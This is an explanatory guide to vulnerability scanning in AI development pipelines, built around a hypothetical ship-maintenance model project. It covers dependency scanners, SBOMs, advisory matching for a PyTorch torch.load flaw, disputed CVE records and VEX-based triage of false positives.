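# Vulnerability scanning of AI development pipelines and their dependencies

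## The parts of an AI development pipeline and the kinds of scanner

Vulnerability scanning is the automated search of software for weaknesses that an attacker could exploit. A scanner compares source code, a list of installed packages or a stored file with records or patterns of known weaknesses, then lists its findings for a person to act on. In AI work, scanners search the development pipeline, which is everything that turns data and code into a released model, including data tools, training and evaluation code, libraries, build and release automation, and model files.

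Outsiders wrote much of that material. A project names some third-party packages as its direct dependencies, and those bring in further packages, called transitive dependencies, that nobody on the team chose. In March 2026, NCSC New Zealand published *Artificial intelligence and machine learning Supply chain risks and mitigations*, joint guidance from security agencies in eight countries. The guidance counts data, models, software, hardware and outside services as parts of the AI supply chain, any of which can introduce a weakness. It starts from the principle that security practices for new software also apply to AI components, then concentrates on what is specific to AI.

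### From raw data to released weights

In a hypothetical project, five engineers want to build a small language model that answers questions about ship maintenance. They plan to train an openly available model further on their own documents (fine-tuning) and publish the resulting weights, which are the numbers in the model that training adjusts.

The engineers begin with two sources of data, a public dataset from the web and several thousand repair manuals in PDF. They can scan the data loaders, the scripts that fetch, unpack, parse and filter these files, like any other code. They can also check the parsing libraries against public records of flaws and run a malware scanner over the downloaded archives. NCSC New Zealand recommends keeping outside data on isolated machines until it has passed such tests. These scans won't catch errors in the text itself, such as a wrong torque value in a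 manual, which makes it bad training data but isn't a software flaw.

The next part of the pipeline is the base model. *Malicious AI Models Undermine Software Supply-Chain Security* lists the usual steps: choose a repository such as Hugging Face, pick a model, install the packages needed to load it, import it, check that its inputs and outputs fit, fine-tune it, test it, save it and deploy it. By the time the engineers measure the model's accuracy, they have already installed new packages and opened a file from someone they don't know on their own machine, so a scan of the model file is useful only if it happens between the download and the first load.

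The training code is probably a few thousand lines, some of them copied from an example that came with the base model. It uses Python packages, including a deep-learning framework, a tokeniser (which cuts text into the units the model processes) and a tool that logs experiments. The package installer can write a lock file, which lists the exact version of every direct and transitive dependency, and the engineers scan this file.

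Many of these packages have a Python interface but call compiled libraries that run on the graphics processor (GPU). Those libraries rely on the GPU's driver and firmware, which NCSC New Zealand identifies as extra places to attack. A scanner can compare a compiled library's version number with public records, but a tool that analyses Python source can't examine the compiled code that Python calls.

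The engineers pack the operating-system files, Python, the GPU libraries and their own code into a container image so that the training run behaves the same on every rented machine. System packages that were current when the image was built may have published flaws three months later. Scanning only the project's Python packages would miss those system packages.

Build automation connects the stages. Short configuration files define jobs that test each code change, build the image, start the training run and upload the result. The jobs need credentials for the cloud provider and the model repository. Anyone who can edit these files can change what goes into the release without touching the training code, so the files are worth scanning for unsafe settings and pasted-in credentials.

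At the end, evaluation code tests whether the model is good enough, and the engineers save and upload the weights. They should scan this file as well as the one they loaded at the start, because their users will also be loading a file that someone else made.

### The records behind a finding

Most findings about third-party code refer to a small set of public records, and reading a scan report requires knowing what each one contains.

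A CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) number is a unique label, such as CVE-2004-2761, that lets people know they are referring to the same vulnerability. Organisations authorised by the CVE Program, many of them suppliers of the software concerned, assign the numbers and publish a record for each. The CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2026), in force since 25 August 2026, require a record to give at least one product that is or may be affected, the type or cause of the flaw, a description and a public reference. They recommend, but do not require, including the version that fixes the flaw.

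An advisory is a public record of one vulnerability that gives the affected versions, the fixed version, the severity and a description. Several databases publish advisories, and most vulnerabilities also have a CVE number. OpenSSF's *OSV Schema* lists the databases that share one machine-readable format, including GitHub's and the one for PyPI, the main public index of Python packages.

An affected-version range marks where in a package's history a flaw begins and ends. In the Go programming language's vulnerability database, a range has an "introduced" version and a "fixed" version, and an "introduced" value of 0 means the flaw was there from the start. If a range runs from 0 to a fix in 2.4.1, version 2.4.0 is affected and 2.4.1 is not. Go's code includes a copy of a shared format for vulnerability data, which can also record the last version known to be affected. This helps when no fix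 exists.

A severity score is a number from 0 to 10, calculated using the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). In CVSS version 3, scores from 0.1 to 3.9 are low, 4.0 to 6.9 medium, 7.0 to 8.9 high and 9.0 to 10.0 critical. *Vulnerability Metrics*, from the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD), warns that the score "is not a measure of risk". The base score describes the flaw itself and does not account for where a team runs the software.

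When a vendor announces a flaw without giving details, NVD assumes the worst and assigns 10.0, so the highest score can reflect missing information rather than known severity. NIST, the US standards institute that runs the database, used to add its own score to every CVE. Help Net Security's *NIST admits defeat on NVD backlog, will enrich only highest-risk CVEs* (April 2026) reported that it no longer routinely does so when the organisation that submitted the CVE has supplied a score. Since many submitters are suppliers, the only score on a flaw may now come from the company whose product has it.

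Deserialisation, the source of much of the danger in model files, means rebuilding a program's objects from a stored file. Some formats, including Python's pickle, allow a file to contain instructions as well as data, so opening the file can run code its maker put there.

### Five kinds of scanner

The tools are easiest to tell apart by what a team wants to know when it runs them.

A dependency scanner, which vendors also sell as software composition analysis (SCA), checks whether any package a project uses has a published flaw. It relies entirely on other people's reports and does not need to analyze the package's code.

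Engineers need static analysis to find dangerous patterns in their own code, because nobody publishes advisories about a five-person team's data loader. Static analysis examines code for faulty patterns or data flows without running it.

Secret scanners look for passwords, keys and access tokens left where others can read them. They have to cover old versions of the code as well as the current one, since a key deleted from a file remains in the project's history.

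Configuration and container scanners check whether the environment is safe, regardless of the quality of the code that runs in it. They check the settings of build jobs, cloud accounts and container images, and list the system packages inside an image.

A model-file scanner checks whether opening a model file would run code, without loading the file. Of the five kinds of scanner, it is the most specific to AI.

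| Scanner | Input | Method | Typical finding |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Dependency scanner | Lock file, or a software bill of materials (SBOM: a machine-readable inventory of components) | Matches package names and versions to advisories | The installed PDF parser is inside an affected range, and a fixed version exists |
| Static analysis | Source of data loaders, training and evaluation code | Searches for faulty patterns and traces data through the program | A file name from a downloaded archive reaches a system command unchecked |
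| Secret scanner | Source files, notebooks, logs, version history | Searches for known key formats and for strings that look random | An upload token for the model repository, in the saved output of a notebook |
| Configuration and container scanner | Build-job definitions, cloud settings, container images | Compares settings with rules, and system packages with advisories | The training container runs with administrator rights |
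| Model-file scanner | Incoming and outgoing model files | Inspects the file's structure for instructions that would run on loading | A weights file that would start a system command |

These kinds of scanner overlap. Many products bundle several of these functions, and a container scanner also acts as a dependency scanner for system packages. A reviewer who reads "we scan everything" in a security report should ask which inputs the tool received, since a product that can scan container images checks only the images it is given.

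NCSC New Zealand recommends general malware scanning, static testing, dynamic testing (running the software to see what it does) and an audit of components. It also names model scanners among the newer AI-specific tools, but cautions that the effectiveness of these tools can be hard to verify and that users should assess it themselves.

### Accidental flaws, malicious packages and insider changes

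Whether a scanner finds a dangerous line of code depends largely on how the line got into the pipeline. Suppose the ship-maintenance project relies on a tokeniser library.

The library may have an accidental flaw that is already on record. For example, its maintainer might have made a mistake two years ago and corrected it after a researcher noticed, and a database published an advisory with the range of affected versions.

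A package can be malicious because an outsider stole the maintainer's password and published a new version that copies cloud credentials from every machine that installs it. The outsider might instead upload a separate package under a nearly identical name and wait for someone to mistype the original. AI libraries have been attacked too. NCSC New Zealand describes a 2024 compromise in which people who installed a published AI library also installed software that mined cryptocurrency.

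In the remaining case, the library is sound. One of the five engineers, who is allowed to edit the data filter, changes it to let a chosen set of documents into the training data. This is an insider change, a harmful change made on purpose by someone with legitimate access. A software agent with permission to edit the code could also make such a change.

Dependency scanners were designed to find accidental flaws that have already been reported. Static analysis, secret scanners and configuration scanners also look mainly for accidental flaws, but ones that nobody has reported yet. Model-file scanners were designed to catch files that an outsider has made dangerous. Dependency scanners can be extended to detect malicious packages once someone has reported them. The databases that OpenSSF lists include a separate Malicious Packages Repository in the same format as ordinary advisories. None of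 the five kinds of scanner was designed to detect attacks by insiders.

The CVE Program forbids its numbering authorities to treat general-purpose malicious code as a vulnerability. They may, but need not, assign a CVE number when someone has altered a legitimate product to be malicious, for instance by adding a backdoor. They should not assign numbers to flaws in products that were never publicly available.

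That last rule applies to a company's private training code. If an insider alters the code, there will ordinarily be no CVE record for a dependency scanner to match. If a public release later includes the altered code, a numbering authority could assign a CVE number, but only after someone had found the change by other means. Static analysis does examine private code and might flag an insider's change that contained a dangerous pattern. The edited data filter contains no such pattern, since it is valid code that does what the insider intended.

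### What differs from ordinary software

All of the above applies, with small adjustments, to ordinary software such as a payroll system, but four features of AI work change how much a scan covers and how hard it is to act on the findings.

Python libraries for machine learning change quickly. A new base model may need the newest release of a library, while an experiment from last month may run only on the old one, so engineers who want to reproduce a result have a good reason to keep the old versions. A finding with an available fix can therefore stay open for a long time even when no one has been careless. The upgrade might break the training run or alter its results, and checking can require another run.

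Pipelines also contain large binary files, such as model weights that take up several gigabytes. Reviewers can't read a change to these files as they would a change to code, and *Malicious AI Models Undermine Software Supply-Chain Security* describes the files as opaque for this reason. NCSC New Zealand adds that attackers can hide pieces of malware among the weights, where antivirus software may not look. Checksums, short codes computed from a file's contents, can confirm that a download matches what the publisher released, but they don't protect against tampering before release.

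Research code also often becomes production code. Someone might write a script for a single experiment, with an access token pasted into the code and no tests. If the experiment works, the same script might be preparing the data for every release six months later. A company that scans only the repositories it regards as products may never have scanned that script.

The last difference, that data as well as code determines what a model does, is the hardest to scan for. A change in a payroll system's behaviour generally comes from a change in code or settings, both of which a scanner can read. A language model can learn new behaviour from its training documents without any change to its code. NCSC New Zealand describes data poisoning, the malicious alteration of training data, as hard to detect in large datasets, especially when the data was compromised at its source. It also notes that poisoning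 can produce a model that misbehaves only when its input contains one particular feature. If the ship-maintenance team used the same code to train two models on different versions of the repair manuals, the code's scan reports would be identical, but the models could give different advice about the same engine.

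## Listing dependencies and matching them to known vulnerabilities

The ship-maintenance team can check every library it installs against a vulnerability database, though the database won't list errors such as a wrong torque value. A dependency scan can still miss vulnerabilities if either the package list or the collection of advisories is incomplete.

### From project file to report

An engineer usually starts with a short project file that lists the packages the code imports and sets loose limits on their versions. For example, the line `torch>=2.0` allows any release of PyTorch from 2.0 onwards. The scan then has five steps.

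1. Resolve the dependencies. A package manager picks a version of each package that satisfies every limit, then does the same for the packages that those packages need. The engineer should run it with the operating system and Python version of the training machine, because the answer can differ between platforms.
2. Write the result to a lock file and keep that file in version control beside the code.
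3. Produce an SBOM from the lock file. Generators such as Syft and Trivy write the two common formats, CycloneDX and SPDX. Some scanners read lock files directly, but an SBOM can accompany the released model, and the team can scan it again next month without rebuilding anything.
4. Query the advisory databases for each package name and version.
5. Report each match with the installed version, the advisory's identifier and the fixed version. The report should also give the scanner's version, the date of its advisory data and the number of packages it checked, because "no findings" means little without them.

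With three widely used open-source tools, the whole procedure can take three commands:

```
uv pip compile requirements.in -o requirements.txt
syft dir:. -o cyclonedx-json=sbom.json
grype sbom:sbom.json
```

The first command resolves the dependencies and records the exact version of each. The second turns the result into an SBOM, and the third matches the SBOM to advisories and prints the findings.

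### Why a requirements file is a poor input

Many Python projects have no lock file, only a `requirements.txt` that someone wrote by hand for pip, Python's standard package installer. This file lists direct dependencies, often with a range of versions. Pip selects the exact versions and any indirect dependencies during installation, and doesn't save a list of them unless someone asks for it.

*A Reality Check on SBOM-based Vulnerability Management* (Zhou, Dacier and Konstantinou, 2026) reports a test on gym, OpenAI's library for reinforcement learning. Gym's requirements file lists 15 dependencies. Syft and Trivy each detected only the 5 that the file fixed to an exact version with `==`, and dropped every entry with a range such as `>=`. The researchers then moved the same requirements into Poetry, a package manager that writes lock files, and ran both tools on the lock file it generated.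 Both listed the same 32 packages.

A team that scanned the original file would therefore have checked only about a sixth of the 32 packages. A vulnerability scan of all 32 found nothing, so the omission did no harm in this case. But Poetry chose the package versions when the researchers ran it, so the scan covered a fresh installation of gym, not the copies people had installed years earlier.

The commands `pip freeze` and `uv pip compile` write requirements files that give an exact version for every package, and such a file can serve as a lock file. A reviewer can recognize one by checking for `==` on every line.

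Zhou and colleagues also ran a larger test, on 2,414 open-source repositories in four programming languages. Of the 243 Python projects, 23 already had a lock file. The researchers tried to generate one automatically for the other 220 and succeeded with only 42, or 19%, compared with 96% for Rust projects. They attribute the failures to the variety of Python build tools and to their decision to use only Poetry, and they expect that uv or pip-tools would handle the rest. The 65 Python lock files, existing and generated, listed 1,997 dependencies. Syft and Trivy found all of them and reported no others.

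This perfect score shows only that Syft and Trivy can copy a lock file accurately, because the researchers used the lock files both as the tools' input and as the correct answer. The packages actually installed can differ from the lock file if an engineer adds one by hand after the file was written, or forgets to update the file. Poetry's lock files also cover several platforms, so they can list packages that a given machine never installs. To find out what a training run used, the ship-maintenance team could run `pip freeze` inside the container when the job starts, save the output with the logs and compare it with the lock file.

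Tools that have to work out the inventory themselves agree far less. *A Large Scale Empirical Analysis on the Adherence Gap* (Wang, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tested six SBOM generators on the full directories of 3,287 repositories in C/C++, Java and Python. Average agreement between tools on which packages a project contained was between 7.84% and 12.77%, depending on the language. When the researchers repeated the test a year later, newer versions of the tools often produced different output from the earlier versions. The study used more tools than Zhou and colleagues did and covered different languages, but the input is probably the main reason for the lower agreement. A generator given a whole directory has to decide which files count, and Zhou and colleagues note that some include folders for tests and build automation while others skip them.

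A third route is to use GitHub, which generates an SBOM from a repository's dependency graph. The graph combines project files, lock files and any lists that a build job submits. *Beyond Compliance* (Bhuiyan, Besbes and colleagues, 2026) compared these SBOMs with those from Syft, Trivy and Microsoft's generator for 10,000 popular repositories. GitHub's SBOMs generally listed more dependencies than those from Syft or Trivy, and the researchers could match them to more vulnerabilities in nearly every language. They caution that the accuracy of those matches depends on exact versions, so a longer list of findings isn't necessarily better. GitHub also listed transitive dependencies only where the parent package had a version, which is another reason to commit a lock file.

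An inventory can fail completely without an error message. Zhou and colleagues found that Syft 1.33.0 and Trivy 0.66.0 both produced empty SBOMs from `package-lock.json`, the lock file of JavaScript's npm package manager, despite their stated support for it. An empty SBOM leads to an empty vulnerability report, which can be mistaken for a finding of no vulnerabilities. The simplest protection is to compare the number of packages in the lock file with the number in the SBOM.

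### What the inventory leaves out

Even an accurate lock file lists only what the package manager installed, and AI projects bring in a lot of software by other means.

A lock file has one entry for a Python package and none for the compiled libraries inside that package. For example, opencv-python, a popular image-processing package, includes its own copy of the FFmpeg video library. If someone finds a flaw in FFmpeg, a scan of the lock file will catch it only if a database also publishes an advisory for opencv-python.

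GPU containers are another gap. Besides system packages, the base image may contain CUDA, NVIDIA's software for running programs on its processors, and sometimes its own build of PyTorch, so engineers have to scan the finished image. Packages in these images can also have different names. OSV's *CGA-739w-3c28-vj3v* (2026), a record from the container supplier Chainguard, covers a package called `py3-torch-2.7-cuda-12.8` and lists the fix in version 2.7.1-r7. A scanner that searched only for `torch`, PyTorch's name on PyPI, would not find this record.

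Researchers also install packages straight from a code repository, usually because they need a feature that isn't in a release yet. The package may then report the version number of the last release even though its code is months newer. The lock file may record the exact commit (a saved state of the code), but most advisories for Python packages give the affected versions as ranges of release numbers, so someone has to check whether that commit includes the fix.

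Notebook dependencies are harder to track because a cell that contains `!pip install` fetches whatever version is current when someone runs it and writes nothing to the lock file. The team could search its notebooks for such cells, or block installations on the machines that train release models.

Pretrained models are dependencies too. In the ship-maintenance project, the base model may appear only as a quoted name passed to a function that downloads it from Hugging Face. No package manager resolves that name, and the lock file doesn't contain it.

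In *Vulnerable Models in the AI Supply Chain*, Nguyen, Le and Babar (2026) measured how often such names refer to models with a known problem. They searched GitHub for the exact names of 16,977 Hugging Face models that the security company Protect AI had flagged in a public database. They found the names of 3,757 models (22.1%) in at least one open-source project, with over 21,000 occurrences in more than 5,000 repositories. One sentiment classifier appeared in 449 repositories, and other people had fine-tuned 24 more models from it. A flag isn't proof of an attack, and the files containing these names may not be in use, but a list of Python packages would miss all of these references.

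An engineer can list models the same way, by searching the code and configuration files for model names. The search will miss any name that the program assembles while running. The list should also record which revision of each model the project uses, because the owner of a Hugging Face repository can replace the files without changing the name.

AI bills of materials extend an ordinary SBOM with entries for models and datasets. They are meant to provide a standard way to record the base model, fine-tuning data, licences and libraries in one document. CycloneDX has supported machine-learning models since version 1.5, and SPDX has had profiles for AI and datasets since version 3.0. A user who hears that a base model or dataset is compromised can check this document to see whether a released model was built on it.

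It is uncertain how many developers produce an AI bill of materials in 2026. Wang and colleagues cite a Linux Foundation survey in which 90% of 341 organisations were either implementing an SBOM strategy or only planning one, but that figure is for SBOMs in general. Public models often lack the facts that an AI bill of materials would need. In *Collecting, Linking, and Assessing Machine Learning Open-Source Software*, Lazarine, Pulipaka and colleagues collected the descriptions of 373,634 Hugging Face models between February 2023 and January 2024. Of these descriptions, 56% gave the library used to develop the model and 5% gave the training datasets. The data are more than two years old, and the models include many abandoned experiments, but a team that builds on a public model will probably have to fill in some of the entries itself or leave them blank.

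### One match by hand

Matching can be difficult when a version number contains something unusual. PyTorch is a good example because many AI projects depend on it and it has a serious known vulnerability, CVE-2025-32434.

The flaw is in `torch.load`, the function that opens a saved model. PyTorch's documentation had described the function as safe with `weights_only=True`, a setting that was supposed to load the numbers and block any code. The researcher Ji'an Zhou found that a file could still run commands on the machine that loaded it.

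Suppose the ship-maintenance team's lock file contains `torch` 2.5.1. An engineer looks the package up in OSV, a public service that gathers advisories from many databases. OSV's *PyTorch* (2025), which comes from GitHub's advisory database, lists the affected package as `torch` on PyPI, with "introduced" set to 0 and "fixed" set to 2.6.0. This means every release before 2.6.0 is affected. The engineer compares the version numbers part by part from the left. The first parts are both 2, but 5 is less than 6 in the second, so 2.5.1 comes before 2.6.0 and is affected. The record also explicitly lists 38 affected versions, ending with 2.5.1.

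The comparison has to treat each part of a version as a number. A script that compared versions as text would put 2.10.0 before 2.6.0, because the character 1 comes before 6. If a flaw was fixed in 2.6.0, the script would wrongly report it in 2.10.0.

Now suppose the container has version 2.5.1+cu121. The part after the plus sign is a local label, in this case for a CUDA 12.1 build. PyTorch distributes these builds from its own download site. Under Python's rules for ordering versions, 2.5.1+cu121 comes just after 2.5.1 and before 2.6.0, so it is inside the range. But it isn't in the explicit list, which has no labelled builds. A scanner that tests the range will report the flaw, and one that only looks for an exact match in the list will miss it.

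| Installed version | Inside the range? | In the explicit list? | Correct reading |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 2.5.1 | Yes | Yes | Affected |
| 2.5.1+cu121 | Yes | No | Affected |
| 2.6.0rc1 (a test release before 2.6.0) | Yes | No | Depends on whether that build already had the fix |
| 2.6.0+cu124 | No | No | Not affected |
| 2.10.0 | No | No | Not affected |

Pip-audit, a scanner for Python packages, can have this problem. By default it asks PyPI about each package, and PyPI has no vulnerability data for releases it doesn't host. When a user audited a labelled build of PyTorch, pip-audit skipped it with a message that the dependency was not found on PyPI "and could not be audited". This message is easy to overlook in the log of an automated job. PyPI's *pip-audit* lists a `--strict` option, which makes the whole audit fail if the tool can't collect a dependency. A team that uses GPU builds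 should turn this option on, then check that its scanner reports PyTorch 2.5.1+cu121 as affected before relying on its other results.

Inconsistent package names cause similar problems. GitLab's *CVE-2025-32434* (2025) lists the flaw under `pytorch`, and a separate GitLab page lists it under `torch`. The package is called `pytorch` in the conda package manager and `torch` in pip, so a tool that reads a conda environment has to treat the two names as the same software. Spelling can also vary. In the gym test, Syft kept `typing_extensions`, while Trivy changed it to `typing-extensions`.

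One flaw can also appear several times in a report under different identifiers. CVE-2025-32434 is GHSA-53q9-r3pm-6pq6 in GitHub's database and PYSEC-2025-41 in the Python Packaging Authority's. OSV's *PYSEC-2025-41* (2025) has the same affected range as GitHub's record, but its severity score is 9.8 under CVSS version 3.1, while GitHub's is 9.3 under version 4.0. Both scores are critical. A team that merges findings from two scanners has to match these aliases or it will count the flaw twice.

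### Choosing a scanner

Five of the most common dependency scanners differ mainly in what they can read and whose advisories they use.

| Tool | Input | Source of advisories |
| --- | --- | --- |
| pip-audit | An installed Python environment or a requirements file | PyPI by default, with OSV as an option |
| OSV-Scanner | Lock files, SBOMs and container images | OSV |
| Trivy | Container images, directories, code repositories and SBOMs | Its own database, compiled from sources that include GitHub's advisories and Linux distributions' security notices |
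| Grype | Container images, directories and SBOMs, often from Syft | Its own database, compiled from sources that include GitHub's advisories, NVD and Linux distributions' notices |
| Dependabot | The dependency graph of a repository on GitHub | GitHub's advisory database |

Pip-audit suits a team checking the Python packages in one environment, because it can inspect what pip installed instead of relying on the lock file. It won't find flaws in the operating system. Trivy and Grype are better for the training container, since they check system packages as well as Python ones. Dependabot takes the least effort for a project on GitHub and can also propose upgrades, but it doesn't scan the rented machine where the training job runs.

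Two scanners can report different vulnerabilities from the same lock files. Zhou and colleagues scanned their 65 Python projects with both Grype and Trivy. Grype reported 148 vulnerabilities in 13 projects, and Trivy reported 109 in 8. The Rust totals were almost identical, at 2,864 and 2,858. They describe near-perfect agreement between the scanners in the small sample they checked by hand, but the Python totals differ by about a quarter. Since both tools started from accurate inventories, the difference probably comes from their databases or matching rules. Some of Grype's extra findings could be errors or the same flaw under two identifiers, so its higher Python total doesn't show that it is more thorough.

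Running a second scanner with different data takes little effort, and when only one scanner reports a finding, it is worth reading the advisory. But a match with an advisory shows only that a package has a recorded flaw, and most matches don't correspond to a real problem in the project. In the 16 projects that Zhou and colleagues examined by hand, 92% of the reported vulnerabilities were false positives.

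Users may also confuse an audit for known vulnerabilities with static analysis and expect protection from flaws that nobody has reported yet. In *Towards a `pip audit` subcommand for vulnerability analysis & management*, a discussion among Python developers, one of pip-audit's maintainers called this confusion the biggest risk.

### Vulnerable packages in language-model repositories

*An Empirical Study of Vulnerable Package Dependencies in LLM Repositories* (Liu, Hu and colleagues, 2025) provides the most direct evidence on AI projects. The researchers collected the public GitHub repositories of 52 large language models, such as StarCoder and ChatGLM, and listed the packages that the code imports. They found 482 packages, 94 of which come with Python as part of its standard library. This method finds only direct dependencies, because a project's own code doesn't import most of its transitive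 ones.

The researchers then looked up every package in the database of Snyk, a security company, and found 890 vulnerabilities. This figure counts all the flaws on record for any version of those packages, not the flaws present in the 52 projects. TensorFlow (a machine-learning framework), Django (for building websites) and Ansible (for configuring servers) together account for 632 of the 890, or 71%. In 2021, the peak year, TensorFlow had 200 of the 239 new records.

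Half of the vulnerabilities had existed for more than 56.2 months before anyone disclosed them. An earlier study by Alfadel and colleagues, covering 1,396 reports, found a median of 39 months for Python packages in general. Liu and colleagues suggest that AI packages get less scrutiny from the community. That may be right, but so many of the records belong to TensorFlow that the comparison may reflect that project's history more than AI software in general. A single TensorFlow release fixed 117 low-severity flaws.

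The researchers also took the release date of the earliest affected version as the date each flaw was introduced, which is wrong if the advisory's range starts too early. The range for CVE-2025-32434 starts at 0, and its list of versions begins with 1.0.0, from December 2018. But the flaw involves the `weights_only` setting, which PyTorch only gained in version 1.13, in October 2022. This record would put the flaw's age at disclosure at more than six years, when it can't be more than two and a half. Ranges that start at 0 by default would push the median up, for Python packages in general as well as for AI ones.

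The study's best-known figure is that 75.8% of the models with dependency files (25 of 33 repositories) had at least one vulnerable dependency. Elsewhere, the paper gives the number of repositories with such files as 30, which would make the share 83%, and the paper doesn't explain the difference. The 25 repositories are 48% of all 52.

The definition of "vulnerable" affects the results more than the choice of denominator. The researchers counted a range of versions as vulnerable if any version in it had a known flaw. A line such as `torch>=2.0` would count, even though someone who installed the project today would normally get a fixed release. Exact versions are better evidence because the installer has to use the version listed. The researchers found known flaws in 19.8% of exact versions and 28.5% of ranges. StarCoder's file, for example, specified version 4.28.1 of the transformers library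 and version 4.65.0 of tqdm, which draws progress bars, and both had known vulnerabilities. The researchers didn't test whether any project actually used the faulty code.

Liu and colleagues also found that only 9 of the 52 repositories had accepted a code change that addressed a vulnerability. Of the 100 such changes they found, 79 updated a dependency. Half of these updates came within 11 days of the fixed version's release, but that figure excludes repositories that never updated.

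The study covers only public repositories, and people often publish research code alongside a paper and then stop working on it. The results can't show whether an AI company's internal pipeline is more up to date or less. It might be more up to date because someone is paid to maintain it, or less because no outsider can point out an old package.

### Missing, late and disputed records

Even with a complete inventory and accurate matching, a scan can miss a flaw because the database has no record of it. The record may be missing because nobody has found the flaw, because the maintainers fixed it in an ordinary release without requesting an advisory, or because the package is too new for anyone to have examined it.

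Vulnerability records also often arrive late. The PyTorch developers fixed CVE-2025-32434 in version 2.6.0, released in January 2025, but the advisory came out on 18 April. If the ship-maintenance team had scanned version 2.5.1 in March, the scan would not have reported this flaw, although anyone who studied the changes in the new release might have discovered it. Liu and colleagues found that 68.9% of the vulnerabilities in their study already had a fix when they became public, so a team that upgrades regularly gets many fixes before its scanner can report the vulnerabilities. For another 28%, the fix came after disclosure, with a median delay of 25 days, and 3.1% never got one.

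The databases add delays of their own. *LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues, 2026) cites research by Segal and colleagues which found that GitHub's review process can delay information developers need. The US National Vulnerability Database has a larger problem, because NIST now adds its own analysis only to the highest-risk CVEs, as Help Net Security reported in April 2026. For the rest, a scanner may have to rely on the submitter's data, which may omit the fixed version, so some records will be hard to match automatically. This probably matters less for Python packages, which GitHub and the Python Packaging Authority cover separately, than for compiled libraries and GPU software.

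More vulnerability reports would make the delays worse, and reports about AI software now arrive steadily. Shifat and colleagues counted 295 GitHub advisories between January 2025 and January 2026 that mention components related to language models. Of these, 162 were for packages on PyPI and 96 were for JavaScript packages on npm, so a team whose model has a web interface should scan the interface's code too. The researchers found the advisories by searching for keywords, because GitHub's advisory format has no field for marking a package as related to language models. AI bug-finding tools may also be increasing the number of reports, but it is unclear by how much.

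Existing records change too. OSV's *CVE-2025-32434* (2025) was last modified in July 2026, more than a year after publication, and now links to a security notice that the Linux distribution Debian issued in December 2025. A scan result is therefore only valid for the day it was made, so the team should rescan a released model's SBOM on a schedule, even if the code has not changed.

Disputed records are awkward because the people involved disagree about whether a flaw exists. The best-known case in AI is CVE-2023-48022, in Ray, an open-source system that spreads Python work across many machines and that many teams use for training. Ray accepts jobs over the network, and according to the record, a remote attacker could use this feature to run any code on the machines. Anyscale, the company behind Ray, rejected the report, arguing that Ray is meant to run code and that its documentation tells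 users to keep it inside a strictly controlled network. The CVE record is labeled "disputed" and includes the company's position.

Password-free access to Ray is reasonable on an isolated cluster but very dangerous on a machine that anyone on the internet can reach, and attackers have broken into exposed Ray servers. An engineer can't tell from the installed version alone which situation the team is in.

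A scanner that leaves out records labeled as disputed will report nothing about Ray, while one that includes them will give the same warning for a safe cluster as for an exposed one. An automated report from PyUp, a company that scans Python packages, includes a PyTorch flaw marked "Disputed". It lists the flaw against version 2.0.1, although according to its description the flaw was found in version 2.6.0.

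The ship-maintenance team should find out which approach its scanner takes, then search for disputed vulnerability records affecting the few systems that accept connections from other machines. If the team uses Ray, an engineer can try to reach the job service from outside the cluster. If the connection succeeds, the team has to block outside access, even if the database lists the flaw as disputed.

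## Deciding which findings to fix and how soon

Whether Ray's disputed flaw is dangerous depends on the network, and many undisputed flaws also threaten only some projects. Someone has to work out which findings matter and fix them before an attacker exploits them.

### Correct matches that don't matter

Suppose the ship-maintenance team's data loader uses Pillow, a Python image library, to shrink scanned pages from the repair manuals. The lock file pins Pillow to version 9.5.0, and the scanner reports a flaw in its `ImageMath.eval` function, which evaluates formulas on images. The installed version does have the flaw, but the loader only opens images and makes thumbnails, so it never runs the faulty code.

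*VEX-BENCH* (Shi, Tsien and colleagues, 2026) collects 75 cases in which a scanner might flag a flaw in a dependency of a popular open-source project. Five people with experience in software engineering and security examined the code and concluded that the flaw affected the project in 22 cases. They sorted the other 53 by the reason the flaw did not affect the project.

In 38 cases, the project had the vulnerable code but never ran it. Nacos, a configuration service from Alibaba, includes a library with a known flaw, but nothing in Nacos refers to the functions that the fix changed.

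In other cases, a setting prevents the problem. Airflow, which many teams use to schedule data jobs, depends on a library with a serialisation flaw, but Airflow's default configuration turns off the affected feature. The environment can also rule out an attack. For example, one flaw requires conditions that the database engine Presto doesn't support. In a few cases, the advisory named a family of packages, and the project used one that didn't contain the vulnerable module.

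The reason a finding doesn't currently affect a project determines what could make it relevant later. If a setting protects the project, the team has to keep anyone from changing that setting. If the project never calls the vulnerable function, one new line of code that calls it could expose the project.

An engineer can record such a conclusion in a VEX (Vulnerability Exploitability eXchange) statement, a machine-readable declaration of whether a known vulnerability affects a product, and why. Suppose the team runs a separate service that answers mechanics' questions. It has PyTorch 2.5.1 installed but loads weights only from safetensors files, a format that can't contain code. In OpenVEX, one of the common VEX formats, the central part of the statement might be:

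```
{
  "vulnerability": {"name": "CVE-2025-32434"},
  "products": [{"@id": "pkg:generic/ship-answers@1.2.0"}],
  "status": "not_affected",
  "justification": "vulnerable_code_not_in_execute_path",
  "impact_statement": "Loads only safetensors files; never calls torch.load."
}
```

The other statuses are "affected", "fixed" and "under investigation". Some scanners can read these statements and hide the findings they cover. But Zhou and colleagues point out that VEX is only a format for communicating a conclusion and doesn't check whether the conclusion is right, so a reviewer should ask what evidence supports each "not affected". Teams also can't expect suppliers to do much of this work. *CAPE* (Podder, Koscinski and Ray, 2026) reports that fewer than 5% of advisories come with a VEX statement, and that a supplier doesn't know how a particular team has set up the software.

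### Nine real problems in 113 findings

Zhou and colleagues based their 92% false-positive rate on a manual check of the 113 vulnerabilities that Grype and Trivy together reported in 16 projects, four each in Python, Rust, Ruby and PHP. They searched the projects' source code for uses of each vulnerable function. Where the advisory didn't name a function, they read the code to judge whether the flaw was present. They confirmed 9 vulnerabilities and counted the other 104 as false positives.

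A single large library can produce many findings that don't affect the project using it. In one Ruby project, the scanners reported ten flaws in activesupport, a large library of general-purpose code. Nearly all involved attacks over HTTP, but the project used a small, unrelated part of the library and never loaded the vulnerable modules.

The researchers then kept only the findings whose vulnerable functions the project used. This left 42 of the 113 findings, including all nine confirmed ones and 33 false positives. The paper reports a 61.9% reduction in false positives, but the counts don't quite match. Removing 71 findings cut the total by 62.8% and the false positives by 68.3%.

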